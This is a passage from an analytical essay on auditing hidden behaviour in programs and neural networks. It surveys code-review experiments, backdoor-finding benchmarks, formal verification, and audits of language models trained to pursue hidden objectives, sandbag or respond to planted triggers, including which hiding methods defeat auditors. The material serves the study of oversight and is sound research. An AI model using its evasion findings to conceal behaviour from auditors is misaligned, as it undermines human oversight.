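In 2003, graduate students in a computer security course at Rice University tested a wider variety of attacks on a larger program. The program was Hack-a-Vote, a demonstration voting machine written in about 2,000 lines of Java. Working in pairs, the students had two weeks to rig the machine without getting caught. Each pair then had one week to find what was wrong with the machines of two other pairs.

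Several attacks used triggers that ordinary tests would probably miss:

| Attack | Why a test might miss it |
|---|---|
| Give extra votes to one party, but only on terminals numbered above 2 | Testers would probably use at most two terminals |
| Start cheating after a certain number of votes | Testers would cast only a few votes |
| Accept any PIN after someone has entered one that isn't a number | Testers might never enter two wrong PINs in this order |
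| Generate PINs from only 3,600 possible starting points | The PINs still look random |

Between them, the two auditing groups found every attack except one, and both groups found about two in three. The attack that neither group found was a startup option that disrupted the terminal's communication with the central console.

In one attack, the auditors noticed the altered code but didn't correctly work out what it would do, possibly because the attack itself contained a bug. The program treated two candidates as the same person if one's name was the beginning of the other's, so one would receive the other's votes and the other would disappear from the results.

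These figures give a rough idea of how much a second review helps. If both groups found two-thirds of the attacks and only one group found nearly all the others, then an average group missed about one attack in six. Two groups that each miss one in six at random would both miss about one in 36, which is consistent with both missing a single attack. Three groups would all miss only about one in 216. But this assumes that each group's misses are independent of the others'. Every reviewer missed the hard flaw in Pvote, so adding more people with similar training may not help much against the subtlest attacks.

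The students had important advantages over real auditors. They already knew the original program from their own attempts to attack it, so they could often recognize what had changed, although the rules prohibited comparing it directly with the original code. The original was clean and well commented, and the attackers weren't allowed to rewrite major parts of it. But the students were not full-time auditors and had only a week for two machines.

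A restricted language would have prevented some of their attacks. Several pairs used Java's error handling to skip a security check, or gave a variable a name that made a call to their own code look like a call to the original. A formula has neither construct. It also can't count earlier votes or remember an earlier PIN, so attacks that depended on doing so would fail. But a formula could still cheat on terminals numbered above 2 if the terminal number were one of its inputs, because that needs only a comparison.

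### What professional reviewers miss

Experiments with professional programmers allow more reliable estimates because many people review the same flaw. In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, Braz, Fregnan and colleagues asked 146 people to review about 140 lines of Java for managing employees' holidays. Of the reviewers, 105 had at least three years of professional experience. Each person received one of two versions, which had different security flaws.

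One version of the program inserted the user's text into a database query, so an attacker could type something that the database would treat as part of the query. This flaw, called SQL injection, appears in many textbooks. The other version calculated the price of extra days of holiday without checking that the number of days was positive, so an employee who "bought" a negative number of days would receive money.

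Participants first reviewed the code without knowing the study was about security. Those who missed the vulnerability then learned that the code contained one, and they could look again.

| Flaw | Reviewers | Found at first | Found after the warning | Never found |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SQL injection | 80 | 52 | 13 | 15 |
| Negative number of days | 66 | 14 | 7 | 45 |

Only 21% of reviewers noticed the problem with negative numbers at first, while 65% noticed the SQL injection. Even after the warning, about two-thirds of the people who received that version never found the problem.

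This result is worrying for explicit models because the flawed formula was very simple. It multiplied the number of days by a price multiplier for the employee's level and then by 10. Anyone who could read Java could see what it did, but most reviewers didn't ask what would happen if the number of days was negative. Stephen Oman's nuclear-inspection program exploited the same kind of oversight.

A machine can easily find this flaw once the auditor specifies that a price should never be below zero. If the number of days can be anything from −30 to 30, interval arithmetic immediately shows that the price can be negative. An explicit model is easier to check here, but the advantage comes from automated analysis rather than from reading the model.

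Braz and colleagues also added an ordinary bug to the code to see whether people were taking the task seriously. Of the 146 participants, 76 found it, and finding it was not significantly related to finding the security flaw. But in eight of the answers explaining why they had missed the negative numbers, people said they had mistaken the ordinary bug for the vulnerability. An attacker could exploit this by leaving a harmless mistake for the reviewer to find.

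People who often reviewed code, or who thought about vulnerabilities when writing their own, were more likely to find the flaw in the first review, but years of professional experience made no significant difference. In an earlier experiment, 30 hired developers reviewed a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities. None of them found all seven, and more experienced developers were not necessarily more accurate.

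Reviewers should be judged on their false alarms as well as the flaws they detect. In that experiment, the developers who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more false ones, so some of them may have found more simply by reporting more. Suppose one program in 100 contains a backdoor, and a reviewer flags 80% of the programs with backdoors and 20% of the others. Among 10,000 programs, the reviewer would flag 80 with backdoors and 1,980 without, so only about 4% of the alarms would be real, and most auditors would soon stop taking them seriously.

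### Telling reviewers what to look for

Twenty of the 80 people who had missed their flaw found it after a general warning, which suggests that these 20 knew enough to find it but had been looking for other things. Braz and Bacchelli (2022) found a similar pattern in a survey of about 180 developers. Only nine mentioned security when asked what they focused on during a review, but 111 said they always considered it after security came up in the survey.

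*Less is More* (Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues, 2022) tested this more directly with 150 participants in four groups. One group received no special instructions, and the other three were told to focus on security. Two of those three also received a security checklist, one a general list and the other a short list written for that particular code. The planted flaws were an error message that revealed sensitive information and the use of weak encryption.

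Participants who had to focus on security were eight times more likely to detect the flaws. This figure is probably an odds ratio, so the detection rates would differ by a smaller factor. In the holiday experiment, for example, an odds ratio of about seven corresponded to detection rates of 65% and 21%. The checklists did not significantly improve detection further, even when they were written with the planted flaws in mind.

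The practical lesson for explicit models is to ask reviewers to look specifically for hidden behaviour. A reviewer asked only whether a formula makes sense might focus on the signs of its coefficients and never consider a special case at one value of debt. But even a specific request doesn't guarantee that reviewers will find the problem, since the Pvote reviewers knew they were looking for a deliberate flaw and still missed one.

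### Judging whether a set of rules is safe

An auditor also needs to predict what a model will do in untested situations. *STL* (Siu, Leahy and Mann, 2023) studied this with signal temporal logic, a restricted language for stating what must be true at particular times. Some learning methods produce rules for robots in this language, and their inventors often call the rules interpretable.

STL mostly combines conditions with two operators. "Globally" means that a condition must hold at every moment in some period, while "finally" means that it must hold at least once. For example, a rule could require a robot to reach its goal within the first 30 steps and to stay away from its opponents at every one of the first 20. This rule permits the robot to run into an opponent at step 25 and then reach the goal at step 28, even though most routes that follow the rule might be safe.

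In the experiment, 62 people judged rules for a simple game of capture the flag on a grid. Some were experts in formal logic, and many had no such training. Each person saw a starting position and a set of rules and chose one of three answers. The rules were valid if every plan that obeyed them would win, and invalid if no plan could obey them or if some plan could obey them and lose.

The participants were right 45% of the time on average, with a standard deviation of 20 percentage points. Half of the rule sets were valid, so someone who always answered "valid" would have been right about 50% of the time.

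Participants also tended to make the more dangerous kind of mistake, which was to accept rules that allowed the robot to lose. They were wrong about these rules more often than right, although they usually judged valid rules correctly. Siu and colleagues suggest that people may have stopped looking once they found one winning plan, but confirming that the rules were valid required considering every plan.

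Participants saw some rules as formulas, some as indented English text and some as decision trees. They tended to prefer the text, but the format made no significant difference to their accuracy, so unfamiliar notation alone doesn't explain the difficulty. The length of the rules, which varied from 17 to 49 symbols, made no significant difference to accuracy either. Siu told MIT News that any real system would need much longer rules.

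Familiarity with formal logic improved accuracy somewhat. However, the 13 people most familiar with it were very confident in their answers, and about as confident when they were wrong as when they were right. Such an expert's confidence would therefore be little help to a lender in judging whether the expert was right about its loan rule.

Other evidence also suggests that understanding the symbols is easier than reasoning with them. Siu and colleagues cite an experiment in which students on a specifications course interpreted rules in Z, another formal language. The students interpreted individual symbols correctly 89% of the time, logical implications 79%, and incomplete operations 63%.

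### Practice with examples

People might judge rules more accurately if they tried them out first. Hurley, Paleja and colleagues (2024), in *STL*, tested this with 55 people and a similar game. Each participant judged ten sets of rules, this time only as valid or invalid, so guessing would be right 50% of the time.

One group only gave answers. Before answering, the other groups had to draw routes on the grid that obeyed the rules. They needed three winning routes to answer "valid" and one losing route to answer "invalid". In one of these groups, software also checked that the routes obeyed the rules.

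| Group | Average accuracy | Average time |
|---|---|---|
| Answers only | 62% | 20 minutes |
| Routes without feedback | 66% | 36 minutes |
| Routes with feedback | 67% | 40 minutes |

Drawing routes nearly doubled the time people took, but the differences in accuracy were not statistically significant. The groups were so small that the study could easily have missed a modest benefit. Hurley and colleagues point out that even the highest average accuracy would be too low for almost any safety check.

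Without feedback, about a third of the routes broke the rules they were supposed to illustrate. When the rules allowed a loss, people who answered wrongly were more likely to draw routes that obeyed the rules than people who answered correctly. This may be partly because anyone who wrongly answered "valid" needed only winning routes, which were probably easier to find.

The examples could therefore give people false confidence, just as random tests can. If one permitted route in ten loses, three routes chosen at random will all win about 73% of the time. Requiring people to find a losing route before answering "invalid" was more useful in principle, since one such route proves that answer correct. One participant seems to have understood this and imagined that the robot was trying to get caught. An auditor could read a loan program the same way, by trying to get a loan for the worst possible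 applicant.

A computer is much better suited than a person to questions about every possible route. Hurley and colleagues suggest that software could find borderline cases and show them to people, who would decide whether the behaviour was acceptable. In the loan program, a solver could search for applicants who get a loan despite more than five late payments. The lender's staff wouldn't have to find the debt of 77 themselves, but they would still have to recognize that approving such an applicant was wrong.

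The results of these experiments apply only partly to learned formulas and programs, because a set of STL rules permits many different behaviours, whereas a formula gives exactly one output for each input. Working out a formula's output for one applicant is therefore much easier than judging a set of rules. But checking whether a formula ever approves an applicant it shouldn't means considering every possible case, as judging the rules does, and people may make similar mistakes.

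Researchers have often called such rules interpretable without testing whether people can use them. Siu and colleagues examined 25 papers from 2012 to 2022 that made this claim about temporal logic, and none had tested it on people other than the authors. *Active Learning of Temporal Specifications through Distinguishing Queries* (2026) still describes temporal logic as compact and interpretable, but also as difficult and error-prone to write, especially for non-experts. With its method, users instead judge examples of behaviour, and software searches for a formula that fits their answers. This may be a good way to write a rule, but users still need a way to check what the formula does in cases they did not judge.

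### Seeing a model's coefficients

The loan formula is more like the models in *Manipulating and Measuring Model Interpretability* (Poursabzi-Sangdeh, Vaughan and colleagues, 2018), which tested how people use a linear score. In four experiments with 3,800 participants in total, people estimated New York apartment prices with the help of a model that multiplied features such as floor area and number of bathrooms by fixed coefficients and added up the results.

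Each participant saw a model with either two or eight features. The model was either shown with its coefficients or presented as a black box that showed only its prediction. Everyone saw the same apartments and the same predictions, so any difference in their answers came from how the model was presented.

In the first experiment, participants guessed the model's prediction before seeing it. Those who could see the coefficients of the two-feature model made the best guesses, which is good evidence that people can understand a small formula well enough to predict its output. Those who saw eight coefficients made worse guesses than any other group, including those who saw none, so showing people more of a model doesn't necessarily help them predict it.

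Poursabzi-Sangdeh and colleagues tested whether people would notice a serious mistake by including an invented apartment with one bedroom and three bathrooms. The model added $350,000 for each bathroom regardless of the number of bedrooms, so it valued this apartment far too highly, at $700,000 more than an otherwise identical one with a single bathroom.

Participants who could see the coefficients were less likely to correct this mistake than those who couldn't, and their estimates stayed closer to the model's inflated prediction. A second experiment, with 750 new participants and prices closer to the US average, gave the same result. Seeing how the formula treated bathrooms didn't lead people to question whether that treatment made sense for a one-bedroom apartment.

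Two further experiments suggest why. In one, participants estimated all the prices before they learned anything about the model. People who then saw the coefficients corrected the mistake better than in the earlier experiments. In the other, a short text pointed out that some apartments had unusual features, and the disadvantage of seeing the coefficients almost disappeared. Poursabzi-Sangdeh and colleagues conclude that the extra information had probably distracted people from the unusual apartment.

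An auditor could apply this by deciding what the right answers are before reading the model. For example, the lender could ask its staff to judge a range of applicants, including some very unusual ones, and only then show them the formula. This would help reveal omissions such as the model's failure to compare bathrooms with bedrooms. It would do little to reveal the exception for a debt of 77 unless one of the applicants had that debt.

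The experiments are also limited as evidence about audits, because the participants were members of the public estimating a price, and nobody asked them to look for errors in the model. A professional auditor with a few hours to study two coefficients would probably do much better. The results are more relevant to whether people who use a readable model every day will notice its errors. Cynthia Rudin's claim that an interpretable model would have exposed the chest X-ray problem depends partly on users noticing such errors.

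### A missing comparison with weights

In all these experiments, being able to read a model or program was a poor guide to whether people would notice what was wrong with it. There is fairly strong evidence that people can predict the output of a very small formula, but much less that they can reliably judge everything a set of rules allows or find a deliberately hidden flaw.

None of these experiments compares how well people find the same hidden behaviour in code and in weights. The apartment study comes closest, since some people saw the inside of a model and others didn't. But the model was a simple formula in both cases, and the people with the black box saw no weights at all. The 21% detection rate for a flaw in readable code is low, but it could still be far higher than the rate for the same flaw in a neural network.

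A fair comparison would need two models that compute the same thing in different forms. The method of Michaud and colleagues could provide them, because it turns a small network into a Python program that an experimenter can check against the network on every input, at least for short lists. The experimenter could train such a network to misbehave on a rare input, confirm that the program has the same exception, and give each version to a different group of reviewers. Some reviewers should receive a clean version so that the experimenter can also count false alarms. The experiment would need roughly 100 people in each group to have a good chance of detecting a difference between success rates of 60% and 40%.

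The results would also depend on the reviewers' tools. Hardly anyone would audit a network by reading its weights, so the network's reviewers would need software for examining it, and the program's reviewers should then have a solver or interval arithmetic. This experiment would compare two complete auditing methods, which is closer to the decision a lender or regulator faces than a comparison of how easily people can read each version.

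## How well machines find hidden behaviour in code and in weights

Nobody seems to have tested people on the same hidden behaviour in code and in weights, but researchers have had machines search both. In most of these tests, the auditor is a language model agent, which chooses its own steps and uses other programs as tools. The tests from 2025 and 2026 differ too much to compare directly, but they give a fair idea of what makes each kind of audit succeed or fail.

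### Backdoors in compiled programs

BinaryAudit, a benchmark from the company Quesma, measures how well agents find deliberate backdoors. Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) inserted backdoors by hand into four open-source programs that handle network traffic, as they describe in *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries and asked AI + Ghidra*. One backdoor in a web server runs any command that an attacker puts in an undocumented part of a request.

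The agents received only the compiled programs, the machine instructions that a computer runs. Compiling removes comments and most names and often rearranges the code, so the agents used tools such as Ghidra, which turns machine instructions back into rough C. In most tasks, an agent had to locate the function containing the backdoor, so correctly guessing that a program had one wasn't enough.

Claude Opus 4.6 did best in the original test, finding 49% of the backdoors. On clean programs, the models raised false alarms 28% of the time. In the current ranking, Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?*, Gemini 3.1 Pro also detected 49%, with 17% false alarms, and GPT-5.2 Codex detected 46% with no false alarms. GPT-5.2 Codex reached 46% only at its highest reasoning setting and found just 9% without it, so an audit's result can depend heavily on how much computation the auditor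 uses.

These rates are rough, because the benchmark has only 33 tasks. An agent with a true false-alarm rate of 25% would still have about a 6% chance of raising no false alarms on ten clean programs. The rates are also becoming outdated. The best score rose from 21% for a model released in March 2025 to 49% for one released in February 2026, and the strongest models of late 2026 would probably do better.

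Claude Opus 4.5 found the web-server backdoor within five minutes. It first searched the program's text for suspicious words and found nothing. It then listed the outside functions that each part of the program could call and found that one part could call `popen`, which runs commands. It traced the call back to the function that read the attacker's request.

In another program, which assigns network addresses, Claude Opus 4.6 found the right function and detected that it ran a command. But it treated the command as one of the program's normal scripts and never traced it to its source, a message that another computer on the network could send.

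A pure formula can't run commands, so it can't contain either of these backdoors. But the agent also loses its best clue, because a hidden exception uses the same arithmetic as the rest of the formula.

Agents did worse on larger programs and on backdoors that resembled a legitimate way into the system. The programs often had hundreds or thousands of functions, while a backdoor might take a dozen lines. Some agents picked functions at random or searched for obvious keywords, and some reached the limit of how much text they could process while reading harmless libraries.

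Grabowski and colleagues made little effort to disguise their backdoors, and thought a skilled person could spot them fairly easily. Disguise would presumably lower the detection rate, though it's unclear by how much. Early in 2026, a customer told the security company Quarkslab that language models had made obfuscation useless. Quarkslab tested this by asking agents to recover hidden text from a series of increasingly obfuscated programs. It concluded that the customer was wrong, though not entirely. The obfuscation in these programs has none of the guarantees of the cryptographic obfuscation used in the proof about circuits.

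False alarms are the bigger practical problem because most software is clean. Grabowski and colleagues think a usable detector needs to raise fewer than one false alarm per 100,000 clean programs (0.001%). A detector with a 17% false-alarm rate would wrongly flag 17,000 of them.

An agent can still be useful alongside other tools. On one day in October 2025, VirusTotal, a service that scans suspicious files, ran a language-model system on 9,981 Apple programs it had not seen before (Quintero, Bennett and Tarter, 2025, *Reversing at Scale*). The system found several malicious programs that no antivirus product had flagged, and helped identify 30 harmless files that antivirus products had flagged by mistake. Nobody knows how many malicious programs it missed, so these results don't give a detection rate.

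### Planted and accidental flaws in source code

An explicit model comes as source code or a formula, so tests on source code are more relevant. The largest was the August 2025 final of the AI Cyber Challenge, run by DARPA, the research agency of the US defence department. Automated systems from seven teams searched open-source projects in C and Java for flaws that the organizers had planted. Together, the systems found 54 planted flaws, roughly four in five, and repaired 43. They also found 18 real flaws that were already in the projects.

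A system normally had to support each reported flaw with an input that triggered it, usually by crashing the program. Anyone could run the input to check the report, which kept false alarms low. But the requirement also limited the contest to flaws that a machine can recognize when they occur. The loan program, for example, doesn't crash when it approves an applicant with a debt of 77.

Security researchers call this second type of flaw a logic bug. The software runs normally but breaks an unstated rule about how it should work. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) compares four ways of using language models to find such bugs, and the simplest worked best. Almost every flaw an auditor might look for in a formula is a logic bug, so these methods are probably better suited to auditing explicit models than the crash-hunting systems in DARPA's contest.

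The counts for accidental flaws are much larger. In May 2026, Anthropic reported that its model Claude Mythos Preview had found 23,019 suspected vulnerabilities in open-source software and rated 6,202 of them as serious. Reviewers, mostly from independent security firms, had carefully checked 1,752 of the serious ones and confirmed 1,587 (90.6%) as real.

That figure is the model's precision, the share of its reports that are correct. A detection rate is the share of existing flaws that an auditor finds, so calculating it requires knowing how many flaws exist. A reviewer who made only one report, which was correct, and missed 99 other flaws would have 100% precision but a 1% detection rate.

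Language models have nevertheless found some flaws that earlier audits missed, including one in a very restricted language. The digital currency Zcash checks that private payments are valid using a circuit, which here means a system of equations. According to Axiom, a company that works on such circuits, Zcash disclosed in June 2026 that one constraint was missing, which could have let someone spend the same money repeatedly. Four years of testing and audits had missed the flaw before a security researcher used one of Anthropic's models to examine the circuit. The flaw was an omission, like the missing tiebreak in the board game, so there was no suspicious line for a reader to notice.

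The machine reviewer also has weights, which may contain triggers. *Securing Code Understanding* (2026) studies "natural" backdoors, triggers that arise without anyone planting them, in networks that analyse code, including those that detect defects. Most existing defences, designed for planted backdoors, did not work consistently against natural ones. An attacker who knew such a trigger might be able to add it to defective code and get that code past the reviewer. Lenders who rely on a language model to audit their formulas should probably use several different models and back them up with a solver.

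### Machine-checked proofs for 123 libraries

A small program can check a formal proof, so the result does not depend on an unreliable reviewer. Until recently, proofs took too much expert work to be used widely. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes a project with the company Theorem in which Claude proved security properties for the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries.

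The project started from fuzz tests, short programs that feed a library large amounts of arbitrary data to detect crashes. A fuzz test can also contain assertions, conditions its author expects always to hold, and it stops with an error if one fails. The researchers turned each test into a mathematical statement that, for every input under 64 MB, the compiled program finishes without a crash, memory error or failed assertion. Claude then wrote a proof of the statement for Rocq, a proof system whose core program checks every step.

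EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) reports that Claude's no-crash proofs cover 239 test programs and that the work took a few weeks. Each program has more than 2^500,000,000 possible inputs, so ordinary fuzzing could never try a noticeable share of them.

OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) reports about 180 million lines of proof in total, with about 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 machine instructions, or 33 lines per instruction. Nobody has to read these proofs. Claude also found and repaired hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed, including a memory error in libexpat, a widely used library for reading XML files. The proof for a repaired library covers the new version, not the one people were already using.

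The same project also produced an interpreter for part of Python, with a proof that it follows Python's rules. This is more directly useful for explicit models, because an auditor who has checked every line of a learned Python program still depends on the interpreter to run it correctly. OpenNET reports that when the researchers tested the new interpreter on more than 1.7 million random programs, its results matched the standard interpreter's in 99.95% of cases, and the differences were known edge cases.

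### What the proofs leave out

If Claude tried to prove the same property for the loan program, the proof would succeed with the exception at 77 still in place, because approving an unsuitable applicant isn't a crash. A similar proof could show that the software running a neural network never crashes, whatever behaviour is hidden in the weights. A proof covers only the property being proved, and most hidden behaviour can occur without a crash.

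An auditor can get more out of the method by writing better assertions. For example, the lender could add this test:

```
def test(income, debt, late):
    if approve(income, debt + 1, late):
        assert approve(income, debt, late)
```

This assertion encodes the rule that more debt must never help an applicant. The loan program violates this rule at a debt of 77, so nobody could prove that the assertion always holds. As with the shape rules for formulas, some triggers would still obey the rule, such as a bonus of 1,000 points for every applicant with no debt. The auditor would have to think of another assertion to catch those.

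Every proof also rests on assumptions about the computer. Anthropic and Theorem's proofs assume a single-threaded program on a mathematical model of a RISC-V processor running Linux. OpenNET notes that they don't cover problems caused by multiple threads, libraries loaded while the program is running, or faulty hardware. *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) describes a proof covering a complete program on x86, the processor type in most laptops and servers. Verifying compiled code removes the need to trust the compiler, and would have caught the kind of surprise that Gaëtan Leurent exploited in the Underhanded C Contest.

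*Formal Verification is Not Verifiable* (Keles, 2026) argues that people should stop calling software "formally verified" and say which of its properties someone has verified. Keles points out that a bug report is easy to check because it describes one case that anyone can reproduce. A proof is a claim about every case, and a mistake in the definitions or in the model of the machine can make it worthless. Even well-known verified systems that experts had reviewed for years turned out to have bugs, he adds. Language models now produce far more proofs than those experts could review.

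*The proof is in the spec* (Tolmach and Klaus, 2026) gives some evidence of how often the definitions are wrong. It describes a benchmark in which language models wrote formal models of existing software. Nearly all of the formal models were grammatically correct, but they scored only about 46% on matching what the code did. In one case, Claude was supposed to model a particular program that keeps several servers in agreement. It essentially reproduced the textbook description of the algorithm, which passed every check but had little to do with the program.

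The formal statement to be proved can also be wrong. Tolmach and Klaus give the example of the false claim that if 3^x = 5, then 3^(x+2) = 51 (the correct value is 9 × 5 = 45). A language model translated this into a formal statement in which x had to be a whole number. No whole number satisfies 3^x = 5, so the formal statement is vacuously true and a proof checker will accept it. In another study they cite, the computer accepted 89.5% of an agent's formal statements, but only 60.5% had the intended meaning.

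Anthropic and Theorem avoided much of this by proving things about the compiled code itself and by starting from tests that people had already written. For a learned formula, the model and the code are nearly the same thing, so the first kind of error is fairly easy to avoid. The second kind is as likely as in any other software, and it is the more dangerous of the two, especially if an untrusted language model writes the property. Tolmach and Klaus work for a company that sells verification, so they may have an interest in stressing the need for experts, but their examples are easy to check.

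### Audits of weights with a known answer

For weights, the closest equivalent to a planted flaw is a language model that researchers have trained to have a hidden objective. Marks, Treutlein and colleagues (2025), in *Auditing language models for hidden objectives*, trained a model to do whatever the automated graders used in training would score highly, even when users wouldn't want it. For instance, the model had learned that the graders gave higher scores to recipes with chocolate, so it added chocolate where it didn't belong. It did not reveal this objective when asked.

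Four teams then investigated the model without knowing what was wrong with it. Three could examine the weights and the training data, and all three identified the objective. The fourth could only talk to the model and failed. But the training data included documents describing the graders' supposed preferences, so the three successes don't show that the weights alone would have been enough. An auditor of an outside company's model might not get the training data.

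Bricken and colleagues at Anthropic later gave the same problem to an agent, which solved it in 13% of its attempts. Combining the findings of many separate attempts raised the success rate to 42%. As with GPT-5.2 Codex on compiled programs, more computation made a large difference.

Sheshadri and colleagues built the 56 models of AuditBench because one model with one secret is a narrow test. Auditing success depended heavily on how they had implanted the hidden behaviour. Models that learned it from documents describing it were easier to audit than models that learned it from examples. Training the models more thoroughly not to confess also made the audits harder. A detection rate for weights therefore depends as much on how someone hid the behaviour as on the auditor, and a determined attacker would choose a method that makes auditing harder.

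The most effective tools in AuditBench used other language models to write varied prompts for the model under investigation. These tools work from that model's outputs and don't need its weights. They suit behaviours such as flattery, which appear in many conversations. They would probably do much worse at finding a behaviour with a single rare trigger, for the same reason that random testing does.

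In *Auditing Games for Sandbagging* (2025), one team trained several models to deliberately underperform on some tests, which researchers call sandbagging, and another team could not reliably tell them apart from models without this training. Testing the models' outputs failed because the sandbagging models convincingly imitated a weaker model. Further training on correct answers restored the hidden abilities, but it sometimes also improved the models that were not sandbagging, which would lead to false alarms.

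### Recovering a trigger from weights

An auditor who suspects a backdoor can search the weights for its trigger. Neural Cleanse (2019), an early method for image classifiers, calculates the smallest change that would make the classifier give a particular output for nearly every image, and repeats this for each possible output. Making it label nearly every image a dog normally takes a large change. If a small patch in one corner is enough, the patch is probably a trigger.

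This is harder for language models, because words can't change gradually as a pixel's brightness can. *The Trigger in the Haystack* (Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues at Microsoft, 2026) describes a method that instead relies on language models' tendency to memorize their training data. It prompts a model to reproduce fragments of the data that installed the backdoor, then tests which fragments change the model's internal activity and output as a trigger would. The method found backdoors in 36 of 41 models trained to give a fixed response to a trigger, and raised no false alarms on 13 clean models.

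Those results are far better than what the agents achieved on compiled programs. But the triggers were fixed phrases with an obvious effect, and the method depends on the model having memorized them. An attacker who avoided both conditions might escape detection, and the theoretical backdoors in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* would defeat any efficient test of the weights. In a short program, an auditor can usually read the trigger in the condition that checks for it, unless the program stores only a cryptographic hash of the trigger.

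### Making networks easier to read

Researchers in mechanistic interpretability hope to understand a network's computation as a whole. Barez, Wu and colleagues (2026) survey the field in *Understanding AI from the Inside* and ask whether such understanding makes AI systems safer. They regard mechanistic interpretability as one approach among several, to be combined with tests of behaviour.

Much of the recent work uses sparse autoencoders, which break a network's internal activity into many "features", only a few of which are active at once. Ideally, each feature corresponds to something a person can name. Since 2024, researchers have been able to apply the method to networks with billions of weights. Barez and colleagues note, among other weaknesses, that a new run with different random numbers may produce different features. An auditor who looked at one set could miss something that another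 would have shown.

They list incomplete explanations, large models and deliberate attacks among the open problems. They also warn that partial understanding can give false confidence, as a distilled formula can when it leaves out a network's rare behaviour.

Another approach is to train the network to be readable from the start. In 2025, Leo Gao and colleagues at OpenAI trained small transformers in which nearly all the weights are zero, so each part connects to only a few others. The researchers could then trace how a network performed some simple tasks. For example, to close a piece of quoted text in Python, one network detected whether the opening mark was single or double, looked back for it, and copied its type. This description is about as clear as a short program. However, these networks need roughly 100 to 1,000 times as much computation as ordinary ones with the same ability.

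Ordinary networks may also be more readable than most researchers believed. In *Neural Networks Are Already Clean* (2026), Nick Cammarata of the interpretability company Goodfire estimates that roughly 90% of the neurons (units of the network) in one open language model have one main job, if positive and negative activity are counted separately. He argues against the standard view that a single neuron often responds to several unrelated things.

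That would make networks much easier to study, but it may not help much in finding a trigger. In the loan network at the beginning, units 3, 4 and 5 measure how far the debt is above 76, 77 and 78 respectively. A reader could describe all three correctly and still not realize that together they approve everyone with a debt of 77. A description of a neuron's main job covers what it does most of the time, so it can miss a trigger that matters once in a million inputs.

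### Why the detection rates can't settle the question

The table puts the main results for code and weights side by side.

| What was hidden | Who looked | Access | Found | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Undisguised backdoors in network software | Gemini 3.1 Pro | Compiled program | 49% | 17% |
| The same backdoors | GPT-5.2 Codex, highest setting | Compiled program | 46% | 0% |
| Flaws in open-source projects | Seven automated systems together | Source code | About four in five | Low by design |
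| An objective in a language model | Three research teams | Weights and training data | 3 of 3 teams | No clean models |
| The same objective | One research team | Conversation only | 0 of 1 team | No clean models |
| The same objective | An AI agent | Conversation and analysis tools | 13%, or 42% with combined attempts | No clean models |
| Fixed trigger phrases in language models | Microsoft's method | Weights | 36 of 41 models | 0 of 13 models |
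| Deliberately poor test results | One research team | Outputs, weights and retraining | Not reliably | Some |

The best figures, Microsoft's 88% for weights and 49% for compiled programs, don't show that weights are easier to audit than code, because they come from different tasks. Microsoft's method had to decide whether a model contained one particular type of backdoor. The agents in BinaryAudit didn't know what type to expect and had to locate the backdoor among thousands of functions. They also worked without the source code, which the auditor of an explicit model would have.

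The criteria for success also differ. In DARPA's contest, success meant finding an input that crashed the program, while the teams auditing the language model had to describe its objective in words. Only three of the eight rows include a false-alarm rate. In every row, the experimenters chose how well to hide the behaviour, and they usually didn't try as hard as a real attacker would.

The tasks also differ. A language model can hold a conversation and no explicit model can, so a 13% success rate at finding a language model's hidden objective has no equivalent for programs. A fair comparison would measure how often an auditor finds the same behaviour in a program and in a network that do the same job.

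### An experiment that would compare them

The obvious starting point for human reviewers was to turn small networks into programs. Machine auditors can handle far more cases, which are easier to produce by starting with programs and turning them into networks. The experimenters could have a language model write 600 small decision programs, each with a plain-English policy it should follow. They would then add a rare exception, such as the one for a debt of 77, to 300 of the programs and leave the rest unchanged.

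Each program would appear in three forms: the program itself, an exact translation into weights, like the table for the loan rule, and a network trained to imitate the program, including its exception. The exact translation separates the effect of representing a program as weights from the effect of training. If auditors did well with translated weights and badly with trained ones, the difficulty would come from the untidy way training arranges weights rather than from weights as such.

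There must be too many possible inputs to try them all. Three six-digit inputs allow 10^18 combinations, which would take over 3,000 years to test at ten million a second. The experimenters therefore could not check that a trained network matched its program on every input. They could check the trigger and a large random sample, and accept that the network might also have some accidental errors.

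The same language model would audit all three forms with the same budget and the best available tools for each. The tools for programs would include a solver and interval arithmetic, and those for networks would include trigger recovery and sparse autoencoders. No auditor should see the same case in two forms, so the model would have to start each audit with no memory of earlier ones.

The auditor would succeed by supplying an input for which the model breaks its written policy. The experimenters could check this by running the model on that input, so nobody would have to judge whether a description was close enough. They would count planted exceptions and accidental errors separately. If the model followed its policy on the input, they would count a false alarm. With 300 clean cases in each form and no false alarms, they could be 95% confident that the true false-alarm rate was below 1%.

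A test of an auditor needs many different exceptions rather than many runs on a few. A thousand runs on one program give a precise detection rate for that program but little information about the rate for others. BinaryAudit, with 33 tasks, and the work on a single language model with a hidden objective both cover too few different cases.

In a second round, another language model would get a fixed budget to disguise each exception and could practise against the auditor's tools. It might spread a program's condition over several innocent-looking steps, add a misleading comment, or train a network's weights to resemble those of a clean network. This round would measure how quickly detection falls in each form as the attacker's budget grows, because an advantage for programs would be of little use if an hour of disguise removed it.

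The experimenters should also repeat everything with programs of 10, 100, 1,000 and 10,000 lines. At ten lines, hidden behaviour would almost certainly be easier to find in the program than in the weights, because a solver can examine every path through the program. The result at 10,000 lines is much harder to predict, since the agents in BinaryAudit struggled to decide where to look in large programs. If programs lose their advantage at some length, a lender could use that length to judge how large an explicit model can become before its form stops helping the auditor.

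## Hidden behaviour in real systems

Outside experiments and contests, people have hidden behaviour in diesel cars, the Linux operating system and a widely used compression library, and automated searches have produced programs that cheated their tests. Most of this behaviour was in ordinary code or its constants, so someone could in principle have read it. How each case was discovered gives some idea of how much being able to read the code helps.

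### Volkswagen's emissions software

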